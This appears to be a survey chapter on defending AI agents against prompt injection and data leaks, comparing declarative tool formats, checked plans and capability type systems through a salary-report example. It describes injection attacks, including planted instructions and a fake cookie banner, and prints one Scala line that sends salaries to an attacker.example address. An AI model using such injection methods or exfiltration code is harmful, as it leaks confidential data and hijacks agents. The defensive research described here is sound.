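When a program takes an email's recipient from a web page, nobody can tell from the code who will get the email. Supporters of declaration propose replacing some code with formats so restricted that a person or a checking program can trace every such dependency before anything runs.

Developers can declare the tools, the plan or both. A tool's declaration shows what it can reach, such as one address on a payroll server. A declared plan shows which tools will run and how data will pass between them. But an agent may call declared tools from an arbitrary program, or follow a declared plan in which each tool is a program that nobody has reviewed.

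### Tools described in a file

Dunkel (2026), in *DADL*, proposes a format for declaring tools. Most MCP servers do little more than pass requests to a REST API, a web interface in which each operation has an address and an HTTP method such as GET or DELETE. Dunkel cites a study of 116 official servers in which 88.6% relied wholly or partly on such an API. Developers normally write and run a separate server for each one. With DADL, they write a file in YAML, a text format for structured data, and one shared runtime reads all the files and makes the requests. A shortened file for a payroll service might look like this:

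```yaml
backend:
  name: payroll
  type: rest
  base_url: https://payroll.example.com/v1
  auth:
    type: bearer
    credential: vault/payroll-token
  tools:
    list_salaries:
      method: GET
      path: /salaries
      access: read
    delete_salary:
      method: DELETE
      path: /salaries/{id}
      access: dangerous
      params:
        id: { type: string, in: path, required: true }
```

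The `credential` line holds a secret's name, not its value. The runtime looks up the value when it makes a request, so developers can share the file without exposing the secret.

The four standard `access` labels are `read` for tools with no side effects, `write` for tools that create or update something, `admin` for privileged operations, and `dangerous` for destructive or irreversible effects. An organisation can add its own, such as `pii` for personal data. The runtime doesn't infer a missing label from the HTTP method, because the result would often be wrong. Many search tools use POST although they change nothing, and a GET request could reset a cache.

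With these labels, an administrator can write one rule for many tools, such as letting every employee call `read` tools, and it also covers tools that developers add later. But the rule works only if the labels are accurate, and the file's author chooses them. The standard labels also don't reflect how sensitive the data is. `list_salaries` has the same label as a tool that lists office addresses, unless someone adds a label such as `pii`.

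### What Declarative Closure guarantees

Dunkel defines a property called Declarative Closure. For any DADL file, the set of HTTP endpoints that its tools can address is finite, and a reader can determine that set from the file alone. The endpoints an agent calls, and the order and number of calls, depend on inputs and data.

The payroll file has two endpoints, counting `/salaries/{id}` as one for all IDs. A reviewer who has read the file knows that its tools can't call any others. Reading the code of a hand-written MCP server doesn't guarantee this in general, because the code may build an address while it runs. Reviewing a DADL file can still take a long time. The public one for GitHub has about 2,700 lines, and Dunkel claims only that a reviewer who reaches the end has seen every endpoint.

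The guarantee covers where requests go, but not what they contain. An email service might have a single endpoint for sending messages, with the recipient as a parameter. The salary report would then use the same endpoints whether the summary went to the managers or to a stranger.

File uploads weaken the guarantee further. Dunkel Cloud's *DADL Specification v0.1* (2026) allows parameters of type `file_url`. The caller supplies a web address, and the runtime fetches the file and passes it to the API. The runtime can therefore contact an address that appears nowhere in the DADL file. An auditor would have to look for these parameters and find out which addresses the runtime accepts.

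### Composite tools and the `read` label

Some jobs need more than one endpoint, such as matching a list of device names with a list of their current states. For these, a DADL file can include a composite tool, a fixed combination of primitive calls saved and offered as one tool. Its author writes the combination in JavaScript:

```yaml
composites:
  clean_salary_list:
    description: "List salaries without duplicates"
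    access: read
    code: |
      const rows = await api.list_salaries();
      const seen = new Set();
      for (const row of rows) {
        if (seen.has(row.employee)) {
          await api.delete_salary({ id: row.id });
        }
        seen.add(row.employee);
      }
      return await api.list_salaries();
```

The code can call only primitive tools from the same service and has no other network access. The runtime allows at most 50 calls and stops the code after 30 seconds unless the author sets a different limit. Declarative Closure still holds because every request goes to an endpoint that the file lists, but a program now determines their order and number. The runtime therefore marks any file that includes a composite with `contains_code: true`, and Dunkel advises reviewers to treat such a file as code. A composite appears in an agent's list as an ordinary tool.

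The example is labeled `read`, but it deletes records. The format doesn't specify what should happen when a `read` composite calls a `dangerous` tool. Dunkel suggests that a cautious runtime should apply the strictest label among the tools involved, while a permissive one may evaluate each label separately.

The reference runtime checks each primitive call against the caller's role and the tool's label. A clerk with permission only for `read` tools would get an error at the first duplicate, and the record would not be deleted. An administrator with permission for `dangerous` tools would delete records by calling a tool declared as read-only, even without meaning to, because the runtime checks only whether the caller has permission.

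These checks also depend on how an operator sets up the runtime, ToolMesh. According to ToolMesh's *Anatomy of an Enterprise Tool Library*, authorisation is off by default to make development easier, and operators have to turn it on for production.

Dunkel Cloud recommends composites for reading and combining data, and advises against using them to write to several endpoints. But DADL's *Use Composites* presents one, from the GitHub file, that copies a repository and then creates a branch in the copy. If creating the branch fails, the copy remains because the code has no step to remove it.

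Dunkel's company, Dunkel Cloud, builds ToolMesh. The paper measures the size of the public catalogue and the tokens that tool descriptions take up, but it reports no experiment on whether agents complete more tasks with DADL. It also does not establish how well the sandbox would withstand a hostile composite.

DADL has no format for a chain across services. The salary report can't be a composite, because the spreadsheet, the web page and the email belong to different services. The agent would still use code composition, writing a JavaScript program that calls the declared tools.

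### Workflows written as data

*A Declarative Language for Building And Orchestrating LLM-Powered Agent Workflows* (Daunis, 2025) describes a format, developed at the payments company PayPal, for declaring the chain itself. A developer builds a workflow from a small set of steps that assign variables, loop over lists, branch on conditions, call functions and send requests to a model. Before the workflow runs, software converts it to JSON and checks for unreachable steps, undefined variables, circular dependencies and tool calls that lack a required field. Because the converted workflow is data, a team can compare two versions line by line or switch between them without restarting the service.

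Daunis compared this system with an ordinary program on 1,000 customer sessions in online shopping, using the same model and tools:

| Measure | Ordinary program | Declared workflow |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed | 78% | 89% |
| Average steps per task | 9.2 | 6.4 |
| Lines of code | 850 | 220 |
| Hours to build | 48 | 16 |
| Hours to add a tool or change the workflow | 8.5 | 2.0 |

These results are promising but preliminary, as Daunis acknowledges. They come from one company and one line of business, and the comparison uses only one program, which may have been a weak baseline. In one example session, the declared workflow needed 6 steps instead of 11, mainly because it ran steps in parallel and chose better branches, both of which an ordinary program can also do.

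The plan also doesn't fully show what some steps will do. In a `toolRequest` step, a model chooses from a set of tools, so a reader can see which calls are possible but not which ones the model will make. A `function` step runs custom code that can contact outside services. Daunis concedes that using custom functions as a workaround breaks the declarative approach. The checks before a run cover only form. The salary report would pass them all, because each variable has a value and each call has its required fields.

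A declared plan also does little to constrain a model that is free to depart from it. *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) tested agents that first committed to a type of plan and then acted step by step. Across three benchmarks, the agents kept to the declared structure in only 22–45% of runs. Software that enforced the structure raised the success rate from 48% to 92% on ALFWorld, a set of simulated household tasks, and from 36% to 44% on SWE-bench Verified, a set of real software bugs.

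### Planning before reading

PayPal's developers write their workflows in advance, but nobody does that for a one-off request such as the salary report, so a model has to write the plan. If the model has already read a hostile web page, the plan may include the attacker's steps.

CaMeL, an agent design that Debenedetti and colleagues proposed in 2025, avoids this by having the model plan before it reads anything untrusted. It builds on Willison's 2023 idea of dividing the work between two models. A privileged model receives the user's request and writes the whole plan as a program in restricted code, which an interpreter then runs. A quarantined model reads files and web pages and returns values, but can't call tools. If the page of pay data includes an instruction to email the salary table to a stranger, the privileged model never sees it.

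*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) calls the resulting property control flow integrity. Text that the agent reads can't add, remove or reorder steps, but it can still change the values that steps use. If the plan takes the recipient's address from the web page, an attacker can put a different address there without writing any instruction.

CaMeL therefore attaches a record to each value, showing where the value came from and who may receive it. Each tool has a policy that checks these records. CaMeL's designers call the records capabilities, but the records only describe data, whereas the capabilities of Odersky and colleagues grant permission to perform an effect. Girrens and Wang (2026) point out in *SPA* that the protection depends on someone writing a correct and complete policy for every tool.

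### The salary report as a checked plan

Girrens and Wang's own system, SPA, replaces these separate policies with a single rule and applies it to the whole plan before any tool runs. The planning model writes the plan once, in JSON, using six kinds of step:

| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
| `retrieve` | loads a result saved from an earlier request |
| `tool` | calls a tool; no other step can have an outside effect |
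| `q-llm` | gives text to a quarantined model, which returns structured data |
| `display` | shows values to the user |
| `condition` | tests a value and runs one of two lists of steps |
| `loop` | runs a list of steps for each item in a collection |

A step's arguments can be fixed values, variables, fields of variables, or lists and objects made from these. The language has no arithmetic, text templates or custom functions. A condition can use one of eight tests, such as "equal to" or "less than", but it can't join two tests with "and" or "or", so the planner has to nest one condition inside another. These limits make every dependency visible. To email an address found on a web page, the planner would have to add a `q-llm` step that reads the page and returns the address. A checker could then follow the data from the page to the email.

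Here is the salary report as an SPA plan. It leaves out the output schema of the `q-llm` step and the notes on purpose and meaning that SPA requires for `tool` and `q-llm` steps.

```json
{"steps": [
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "read_file",
   "inputs": {"path": "/finance/pay/2026.csv"},
   "output": "pay"},
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "fetch_url",
   "inputs": {"url": "https://stats.example.org/pay"},
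   "output": "page"},
  {"type": "q-llm",
   "inputs": [{"var": "pay"}, {"var": "page"}],
   "prompt": "Compare our pay with the industry figures.",
   "output": "summary"},
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "send_email",
   "inputs": {
     "to": "managers@example.com",
     "body": {"attr": {"var": "summary", "path": ["text"]}}},
   "output": "receipt"}
]}
```

SPA gives every value two labels. Confidentiality (*C*) records how sensitive the value is, and integrity (*I*) records how far the system can trust it. Whoever deploys the agent defines the levels. Suppose that the company uses two of each, with public below confidential and untrusted below trusted. When a step combines two values, the result takes the higher confidentiality and the lower integrity:

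(*C*₁, *I*₁) combined with (*C*₂, *I*₂) = (max(*C*₁, *C*₂), min(*I*₁, *I*₂))

A tool has a maximum confidentiality and a minimum integrity for its inputs. SPA allows a call only if

*C*(input) ≤ *C*max(tool) and *I*(input) ≥ *I*min(tool).

The checker works through the plan in order. Fixed values in the plan, such as the file path, take the labels of the user's request, which here are public and trusted. With plausible settings for each tool, the check goes like this:

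| Step | Labels of the inputs | What the step accepts | Labels of the result |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_file` | public, trusted | up to confidential; trusted only | confidential, trusted |
| `fetch_url` | public, trusted | public only; trusted only | public, untrusted |
| `q-llm` | confidential, untrusted | anything | confidential, untrusted |
| `send_email` | confidential, untrusted | public only; trusted only | none, because the check fails |

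The confidentiality check fails at `send_email` because the summary draws on the salaries. The integrity check fails there too, because the summary also draws on a web page that anyone might have altered. SPA rejects the whole plan, so the agent never opens the spreadsheet. The quarantined model might have written a harmless summary with no salary figures, but the checker runs before the summary exists, so it has to assume that the summary could reveal salaries or carry altered text from the web page.

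SPA applies its rule to decisions as well as data. Suppose the plan emails a fixed message, "Pay review needed", only if the median salary is below the industry figure. The message contains no salaries, but the recipient can infer from its arrival how the company's pay compares with the industry's. SPA therefore adds a condition's labels to every step that depends on it, so this email would also fail the check.

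The settings apply to the whole tool, so exceptions are awkward. If the payroll team may see the figures, the company could create a second email tool that accepts confidential data and sends only to that team. The integrity check would still reject the summary because of the web page. The company could let the tool accept untrusted data, but it would then accept an untrusted recipient as well as an untrusted body, unless its code fixed the recipient. Girrens and Wang suggest that future versions could set requirements for each argument, or let a plan raise a value's integrity after an explicit check.

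### What the checks cost

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 simulated tasks in office work, Slack, travel and banking. They also ran 949 trials in which an attacker placed hostile text in the tools' output. With the plan fixed in advance but no label checks, the agent completed 53.0% of tasks when there was no attack, and four of the 949 attacks succeeded (0.4%). In all four, the quarantined model read hostile text and its output reached a banking tool, which made three unauthorised transfers and one password change. Adding the label checks stopped all four attacks but reduced task completion to 29.0%. Just over half of the runs ended because the checker rejected the plan, usually because it passed a tool's output to an action that required trusted data.

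Fixing the plan seems to have given most of the protection, but the experiment can't establish this because it had no ordinary agent for comparison. Nobody knows how many of the attacks would have succeeded without SPA. The attacks also relied on planted instructions, which a fixed plan is good at resisting. An attack that changed the account number on an invoice would test the labels more. The planner was a small model, GPT-5.4 nano. A stronger one might complete more tasks, but it couldn't avoid a rejection when the task itself requires acting on untrusted data.

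SPA also keeps labels between requests, so a confidential summary is still confidential when a later plan retrieves it. It saves the result of each `tool` and `q-llm` step and shows later planners only a description of it. In a version of the benchmark that spread each task over several requests, later plans retrieved the saved result they needed in 95.4% of cases where one existed, or 89.9% with label checks.

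The planner reads the descriptions of installed tools, so a malicious tool could influence the plan through its description. SPA has an optional mode that hides these descriptions. In this mode, the model invents tools that would suit the task, and another step matches them to real ones. Matching failed in about three-quarters of runs, and the agent completed only 14.1% of tasks even without label checks.

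### When the next step depends on what the agent finds

Suppose the salary spreadsheet contains only a note that this year's figures are now in the HR system. An agent that makes one call at a time can read the note and then check the HR system. An SPA plan can test whether the figures are present and tell the user if they aren't, but it can't include a step for checking the HR system, because the planner had no reason to expect the figures to be there. Letting the note add that step would also let an attacker add steps by planting a note.

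Girrens and Wang accept this limit. The planner runs once per request, and a failed check or tool call ends the request. The planner isn't given the reason a plan was rejected, because it could then keep revising an unsafe plan until it passed. It's unclear how many tasks fail because of this rigidity, since the 47% that failed without label checks also include tasks for which the model wrote a wrong or incomplete plan.

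Foerster and colleagues instead try to anticipate what the agent might find. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking, where surprises are common. The planner writes a program that branches on yes-or-no questions such as "Is a cookie banner visible?", which quarantined models answer by looking at the screen as the program runs. The average plan had 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. Roughly half of each plan consisted of fallback steps that a given run didn't use.

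This agent retained up to 57% of a strong undefended agent's performance when a task counted as solved if any of five attempts succeeded. With one attempt, it solved 28% of the same 109 tasks. It used 1.88 times as many tokens as an undefended agent. Foerster and colleagues also tried planning one action at a time while hiding the tools' output. That solved about as many tasks within five attempts but took 29.6 times as many tokens, because the planner had to reread the full history at every step.

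Extra branches make a plan more flexible but harder to inspect, and they give an attacker more to exploit. In one of Foerster and colleagues' attacks, an advertisement imitated a cookie banner. The plan had a step for clicking such banners, so the agent clicked the advertisement and landed on the attacker's site without departing from the plan. A person who approved the plan beforehand would have seen only a sensible step for dealing with cookies.

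Another answer is to write a full plan and revise it only if a step fails. *Do Agents Need to Plan Step-by-Step?* (Otani, Bhutani and colleagues, 2026) compared this with planning one call at a time, on about 3,000 questions that agents had to answer from databases or Wikipedia. Step-by-step planning used two to three times as many tokens, and the paper found no evidence that it was more accurate. This suggests that agents can plan many lookups in advance, but the tasks were well defined, and step-by-step planning might still be better for exploratory work. The planner receives earlier tool results when it revises a plan, so this method doesn't protect it from hostile text in those results.

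*Kaer* (Mallick, Rose and colleagues, 2026) allows the plan to be revised but restricts what the planner can learn. It is for systems in which a planner divides a task among several agents, any of which might be malicious. The planner starts with a minimal plan. An agent that fails chooses a reason from a fixed list, and the planner sees no other text from it. The planner can then change the remaining steps using a fixed set of edits, and the new plan must satisfy the same policies as the original. If the list had an entry for missing data, the agent with the salary spreadsheet could choose it, and the planner might assign the search to another agent. The first agent could not tell the planner that the figures had moved to the HR system.

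On a benchmark that Mallick and colleagues built for the purpose, Kaer blocked 92.3% of attacks with one model and 88.0% with another. An undefended system blocked 35.0% and 47.8%. ControlValve, an earlier defence that keeps agents within limits set at the start, blocked 69.8% and 80.4%. Kaer also completed more ordinary tasks, 64.3% and 65.7% against ControlValve's 54.3% and 34.3%. Kaer's plans are less detailed than SPA's. Each step is a plain-English instruction to an agent with certain permissions, so a reviewer can see which tools the agent may use but not which calls it will make. Kaer isn't designed to stop an agent from misusing the tools that its step permits.

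PayPal's language and DADL leave unexpected cases to a model's choices or to custom code. Neither Daunis nor Dunkel measured how often developers rely on either, or how much harder this makes a review. Dunkel lists where declaration should end and code begin as an open question. Wherever that boundary is set, the code can pass a salary from one call to the next without the declaration showing it.

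## The case for a type checker that limits composed code

SPA can trace a salary through a plan because its plans have only six kinds of step. Odersky and colleagues instead let the agent write real programs, with loops, recursion and its own functions. The language's compiler works out what each piece of code can affect and rejects any code that could break the rules, so that code never runs.

A sandbox alone can't provide this protection. In the salary report example, it would allow both the file read and the email, but the leak comes from passing data from one to the other.

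### Permission as an object

In most programming languages, any code can open a file if it knows the file's name. A Python function called `format_table` might read the salary spreadsheet, even though nothing in its name or parameters suggests that it does. In an object-capability language, code also needs an object that grants access, called a capability, such as an open folder or a connection to a mail server. Code can't create a capability from a file name or a guess, so another part of the program has to pass it in.

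Capabilities date from the 1960s, and designers have since built them into operating systems, hardware and programming languages. Here is a function that receives one:

```scala
def writeReport(folder: FileSystem^) =
  val f = folder.access("report.txt")
  f.write("The pay review is finished.")
```

The function can write to files in `folder` because its caller passed in that object, but it can't send email because it received no object for that.

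With ordinary types, though, `writeReport` could return a function that keeps a reference to `f`. That function's type would show that it accepts a string, but not that it can write to a file.

### Capture checking and local purity

Capture checking, an experimental feature of the language Scala 3, closes this gap by adding capabilities to types:

| Type | What a function of this type can do |
|---|---|
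| `String -> Unit` | accept a string, but use no capabilities |
| `String ->{f} Unit` | accept a string and use the capability `f` |
| `String => Unit` | accept a string and use any capability |

`Unit` means the function returns nothing useful. The compiler works out the list in braces from the function's code. The list may include a capability that a particular run never uses, but it can't omit one that the function might use.

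A function with an empty list is pure, which means that it has no side effects. Odersky and colleagues use the term local purity for the ability to require this of one part of a program while the rest acts normally. They use it to protect secret data, which they put in a container:

```scala
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

A `Classified[String]` is a container whose string the agent's program can't take out. The program can only pass a function to `map`, which applies it to the string and puts the result in a new container. Because `map` requires a pure function (`T -> U`), that function can count rows or calculate a median, but it can't send anything out.

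The compiler also limits how long a program can keep a capability. For example, a program may receive access to a folder for one block of code. If the block returns a function that would read the folder later, the compiler rejects the code, because the function's type would have to list a capability that doesn't exist outside the block.

### The salary report, accepted and rejected

Odersky and colleagues built these ideas into TACIT, an MCP server that runs an agent's Scala code only if it compiles. An operator marks certain files as classified. TACIT also has a `chat` function that sends text to a second model, which the operator runs locally and trusts with secrets. The reply to any classified text is also classified.

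This version of the salary report compiles, assuming that the operator has marked the spreadsheet's folder:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/finance") {
  requestNetwork(Set("stats.example.org")) {
    val pay  = readClassified("/finance/pay/2026.csv")
    val page = httpGet("https://stats.example.org/pay")
    val summary = chat(pay.map { p =>
      s"Compare our pay with the industry figures.\n$p\n$page"
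    })
    writeClassified("/finance/pay/summary.txt", summary)
  }
}
```

The function inside `map` uses `page`, but `page` is just a string, so the function is still pure. The summary goes into another classified file.

Now suppose the operator also provides `mailer`, a capability for sending email to the managers' list, and the agent replaces the last step with this:

```scala
summary.map { text => mailer.send(text) }
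```

The compiler would reject the program with an error like this one:

```text
Found:    (text: String) ->{mailer} Unit
Required: String -> Unit
Capability `mailer` cannot flow into capture set {}.
```

The function needs `mailer`, but `map` accepts only functions that need no capabilities. `mailer.send(summary)` would also fail, because `send` expects a `String` and `summary` is a `Classified[String]`. In both cases, TACIT rejects the code before opening the spreadsheet, and the agent gets the error message and can try again.

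Like SPA's checker, the compiler checks the program before the summary exists, so it would block even a harmless summary. The user can still read the summary, because when a program prints a classified value, TACIT shows the real text to the user and `Classified(****)` to the agent. As with SPA, the company could add an email tool for the payroll team alone. In TACIT, that tool would accept a `Classified[String]`.

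### Tests of safety and task success

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, making 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to have authority to see them. They ran everything with and without the `Classified` container and counted a leak whenever secret content appeared in the agent's output:

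| Model | Kind of trial | Leaks with the container | Leaks without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 8 |

The container made the largest difference when the user was the attacker. The injections were a weak test of the container because they rarely worked even without it. The agents remained useful with the container. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with it and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Sonnet may have scored lower without the container because it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

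On AgentDojo, the benchmark that Girrens and Wang used for SPA, one of 1,926 attacks counted as successful. The agent had booked the right hotel but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another. Odersky and colleagues reasonably blame the benchmark's scoring, which looks for certain words. They also describe TACIT's task completion as comparable to CaMeL's, which is generous. With the model o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of office tasks and CaMeL completed 81.4%. CaMeL also led in the other three areas. With Gemini 2.5 Pro the results were mixed, and TACIT was far ahead on travel tasks (64.3% against 1.4%).

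Writing typed code changed agents' benchmark scores only slightly. On the airline and retail parts of τ²-bench, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala than when they made ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software bugs, MiniMax fell from 43.3% to 41.7%. At most 7.9% of the τ²-bench programs needed another attempt because of compile errors, and those usually needed only one or two. But the τ²-bench tools returned ordinary data, not classified data, so that test didn't measure how well agents work with secrets they can't see.

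### Scope as a list of permissions

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, let permissions vary from one point in a program to another. The work comes from the same university in Lausanne and shares several authors with TACIT. A developer writes a Scala program and leaves holes for a model to fill:

```scala
def draft(pay: Classified[String], page: String): Classified[String] =
  agent("Compare our pay with the industry figures")

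def report(pay: Classified[String], page: String, mailer: Mailer^) =
  val summary = draft(pay, page)
  mailer.send("The pay summary is ready.")
  summary
```

When the program reaches `agent`, the model receives the task, the surrounding source code and the type of result the program needs. It writes code for the hole, and the compiler checks that code as if a developer had typed it there. The model's code can use only the names in scope at that point. In `draft` these include `pay` and `page` but not `mailer`, so the model can't send any email, even one without salaries. The developer's code in `report` sends the notice.

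The compiler accepts or rejects the model's code as a whole. In one of the paper's examples, the code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the code before any of it runs, so the balance stays at 100. Code that passes the compiler's checks can still fail while running and leave a job half done.

LACUNA has no safety proof of its own and relies on the soundness of Scala's compiler. Zhao and colleagues tested their implementation on about 400 pairs, each made up of a program with a hole and code to fill it. Some pairs were valid and others contained common mistakes, and the compiler correctly accepted or rejected each one.

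Both models tested solved fewer tasks with LACUNA than with ordinary tool calls. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. That gap is 14 points, and it widens to 22 on retail tasks, though the paper's abstract describes the result as "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's attempts on retail tasks and 89% of Gemini's on telecom tasks. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen too little Scala in training and expect fine-tuning to help.

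These results conflict with the small gains that Odersky and colleagues found on the same benchmark. The studies used different models and ran each conversation differently, and LACUNA had only one attempt at each task. It is therefore unclear how much of the loss came from the type checker.

On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded, seven of them against Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that the compiler can't stop an attacker from misusing a capability that the task needs. If a hole needs `mailer` to send a legitimate message, hostile text on a web page could cause the model to send a different one.

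### Rules about the order of operations

Capture checking can show that code is able to send email, but not that it asks for approval first. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang et al., 2026) proposes a new language that checks such rules. One of its motivating cases is a bug report about Goose, an open-source agent. A user had required approval for sensitive tools, but when Goose delegated work to a second agent, that agent ran those tools without asking.

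In ETAS, a function's type lists its effects, which are the outside operations that it may request. A separate specification can restrict their order. Here is the end of the salary report in ETAS's notation:

```text
spec ApprovedSend = Approval.request >> Mail.send;

flow send_report(summary: string) -> unit
    ![Approval.request, Mail.send] ~ ApprovedSend {
  if perform Approval.request(summary) {
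    perform Mail.send(summary);
  }
}
```

The list after `!` contains the function's effects, and `>>` means that a request for approval must come before any request to send.

The compiler treats each run as a sequence of requests. Let *a* be a request for approval and *s* a request to send. The specification permits the empty sequence and any sequence that begins with *a*. The code above can produce *a* if the person refuses, or *as* if the person agrees. The code satisfies the specification if

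Pref(*A*) ⊆ *P*,

where *A* is the set of sequences that the code might produce, Pref(*A*) contains all of their beginnings, and *P* is the set of permitted sequences. The beginnings matter because a run may stop partway. There are three possible outcomes:

| What the code might do | What the compiler does |
|---|---|
| *a* or *as* | accepts the code, having proved that it follows the rule |
| *sa* | rejects the code |
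| *as* or *sa*, depending on a condition | accepts the code but adds a monitor, which blocks *s* if it comes first |

The compiler combines these sequences across function calls, so delegating the email to another agent wouldn't avoid the rule. The rule also applies in a dry run, where developers can replace `Mail.send` with a handler, a piece of local code that simulates sending the message. Other languages with effect types usually drop an operation from a function's type once a handler deals with it. But ETAS keeps a second record of every request, so a program that tries to send without approval still fails the check.

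Tan and colleagues prove that a program performs only the operations in its list of effects and makes its requests in the specified order. The proofs cover a simplified core of the language, not the team's compiler. They also assume that every outside operation goes through the host, the trusted program that carries out requests.

The order rule only requires the code to request approval before sending, even if approval is refused. If the developer deleted the `if`, the code would send the email regardless of the answer and still satisfy `ApprovedSend`. A single request would also satisfy the rule for any number of later emails. Tan and colleagues assign these checks to the host, which must confirm consent for the particular operation before carrying it out. ETAS also doesn't track secret data, so it can't show the person approving the email that the summary came from the salary spreadsheet.

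The safety tests were small. Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent in ETAS and tested the part that decides what to read, using 10 scenarios with scripted model replies. It completed four and stopped where it should have in the other six. The compiler accepted two valid test programs and rejected four with deliberate violations. These tests confirm that the checks work in simple cases, but they didn't include live attacks.

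Another experiment let agents revise their own code while the specifications stayed fixed. Over five revisions, accuracy on 256 financial questions rose from 69.9% to 78.9%. This suggests that agents can improve their code under fixed specifications, although the experiment did not measure safety.

### What the compiler takes on trust

The compiler checks the agent's code, but it relies on the people who write the tool wrappers, the functions that connect Scala programs to outside tools. Suppose a developer gives `fetchUrl` the type `String -> String`, forgetting that a web request is an outside effect. This line would then compile:

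```scala
pay.map { p => fetchUrl("https://attacker.example/?pay=" + p) }
```

It would send the spreadsheet's contents to an attacker as part of a web address.

TACIT includes a deliberate exception of this kind. In the AgentDojo tests, a function called `prompt` sent text to another model, yet agents could call it inside `map` as if it were pure. The compiler can't check whether that model's operator stores the text or passes it on. Odersky and colleagues leave that judgment to whoever sets up the system.

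Someone also has to mark the sensitive files. According to Glama's *TACIT*, a later copy of the project's documentation, the default list covers places that usually hold keys and passwords, such as `.ssh` and `.env`. It doesn't cover a salary spreadsheet in `/finance/pay`. Unless the operator adds that folder, the agent can read the salaries as an ordinary string, and `mailer.send` will accept them.

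The later version also intentionally lets programs send secrets out, through a function called `httpPostClassified` that sends classified data to an approved web server and keeps the reply classified. Operators can set a list of approved servers. If they don't, the only list is the one in the agent's own `requestNetwork` call, so a hostile program could apparently approve the attacker's server and send the salaries there.

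The guarantee depends on the agent's code staying within safe mode, a restricted form of Scala that excludes features that could stop the compiler from tracking a capability. Machine-checked proofs cover the basic type system, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs a proof. In the version that lampepfl's *TACIT* documents, the software enforced safe mode by searching the code for forbidden patterns, which is weaker than a compiler check. The later version can use the compiler's own check, but its documentation is inconsistent about whether this is on by default. Operators also need to turn off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and web pages, or the agent can bypass Scala.

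The type system can't prevent some leaks even when it is set up correctly. A program could run longer if the median salary is above a certain amount, so anyone timing it would learn whether it is. If a program starts an external command, the compiler can't check what that command does. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox.

Odersky and colleagues argue that TACIT takes fairly little work to adopt. Its shared library has about 1,000 lines, and the wrappers for each τ²-bench area have a few hundred, roughly as many as the JSON schemas they replace. People can review code of this size once, before the agent starts, instead of reviewing every program the agent writes, which is an advantage over approval prompts. Odersky and colleagues add that only the shared library requires expertise in Scala, but this is doubtful. The mistake in `fetchUrl`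 is a missing capability in a wrapper, and a reviewer who didn't know capture checking could easily miss it.

### Permitted but wrong

The accepted version of the salary report can still mislead its readers. The web page might contain an instruction to report that the company pays 20% above the industry average. If the trusted model followed it, the program would save a false summary without breaking any rule. `Classified` keeps data secret but doesn't keep it accurate. By default, an agent can overwrite a classified file with its own text, although operators can turn this off.

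Odersky and colleagues reply that correctness is a separate problem. They want to limit the damage an agent can do, whether it is hostile, confused or careless, because they expect companies to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision. At that scale, they argue, simple mistakes will lead to serious security failures. Zhao and colleagues likewise accept that "well-typed is not correct" and still recommend tests or human review. They propose adding refinement types, which can require a result to have certain properties. For example, a type could require the median salary to lie between the lowest and highest salaries in the spreadsheet. That would catch some calculation errors, but it couldn't establish whether the user wanted all the managers to see the result.

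## What a larger library of composable tools adds

Each added tool can take part in many chains, so the number of conceivable chains grows much faster than the library. With 20 tools, an agent could make three calls in 20 × 20 × 20 = 8,000 sequences, counting those that repeat a tool. With 40 tools, there would be 64,000. Most of these sequences are useless because they include a tool that can't use the previous tool's output.

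### Counting the chains that fit

Suppose the salary agent has six tools, each with one input and one output:

| Tool | Input | Output |
|---|---|---|
| `find_file` | topic | file path |
| `search_web` | topic | web address |
| `read_file` | file path | text |
| `fetch_url` | web address | text |
| `summarize` | text | text |
| `send_email` (always to the managers) | text | receipt |

These six tools allow 6³ = 216 sequences of three calls, but only 10 are sequences in which each output has the type the next tool needs. One of the 10 is `find_file`, `read_file`, `summarize`. Another runs `summarize` three times, so a chain can have matching types and still be pointless. The count depends on how precise the types are. JSON schemas often describe topics, paths, addresses, text and receipts as strings, and a checker that treated them all as the same type would accept all 216 sequences.

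A new tool adds more chains if many others can connect to it. A `translate` tool, which takes text and returns text, would raise the number of three-call chains from 10 to 30. A `delete_file` tool, which takes a path and returns a receipt, would add none.

Suppose a fraction *p* of ordered pairs of tools fit together, each independently of the others. A library of *n* tools then allows about *n*³*p*² chains of three calls. If one pair in ten fits, 20 tools allow about 80 chains, compared with 8,000 if every pair fits. Doubling the library still multiplies the number of chains by eight, as long as *p* stays the same.

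*In-N-Out* (Lee, Kim and Jo, 2025) counted how many pairs of outputs and inputs fit together in two real collections of tools. The larger has 457 operations from nine simulated apps for shopping, payments, music and similar jobs. Software first removed implausible pairs, then two experienced developers judged the rest. They found that 1.7% of the larger collection's 1.9 million possible pairs would work in realistic use, and 0.7% in the smaller one. About half of the working pairs work only sometimes. For example, the text of a note can supply a recipient for an email only if it contains an address.

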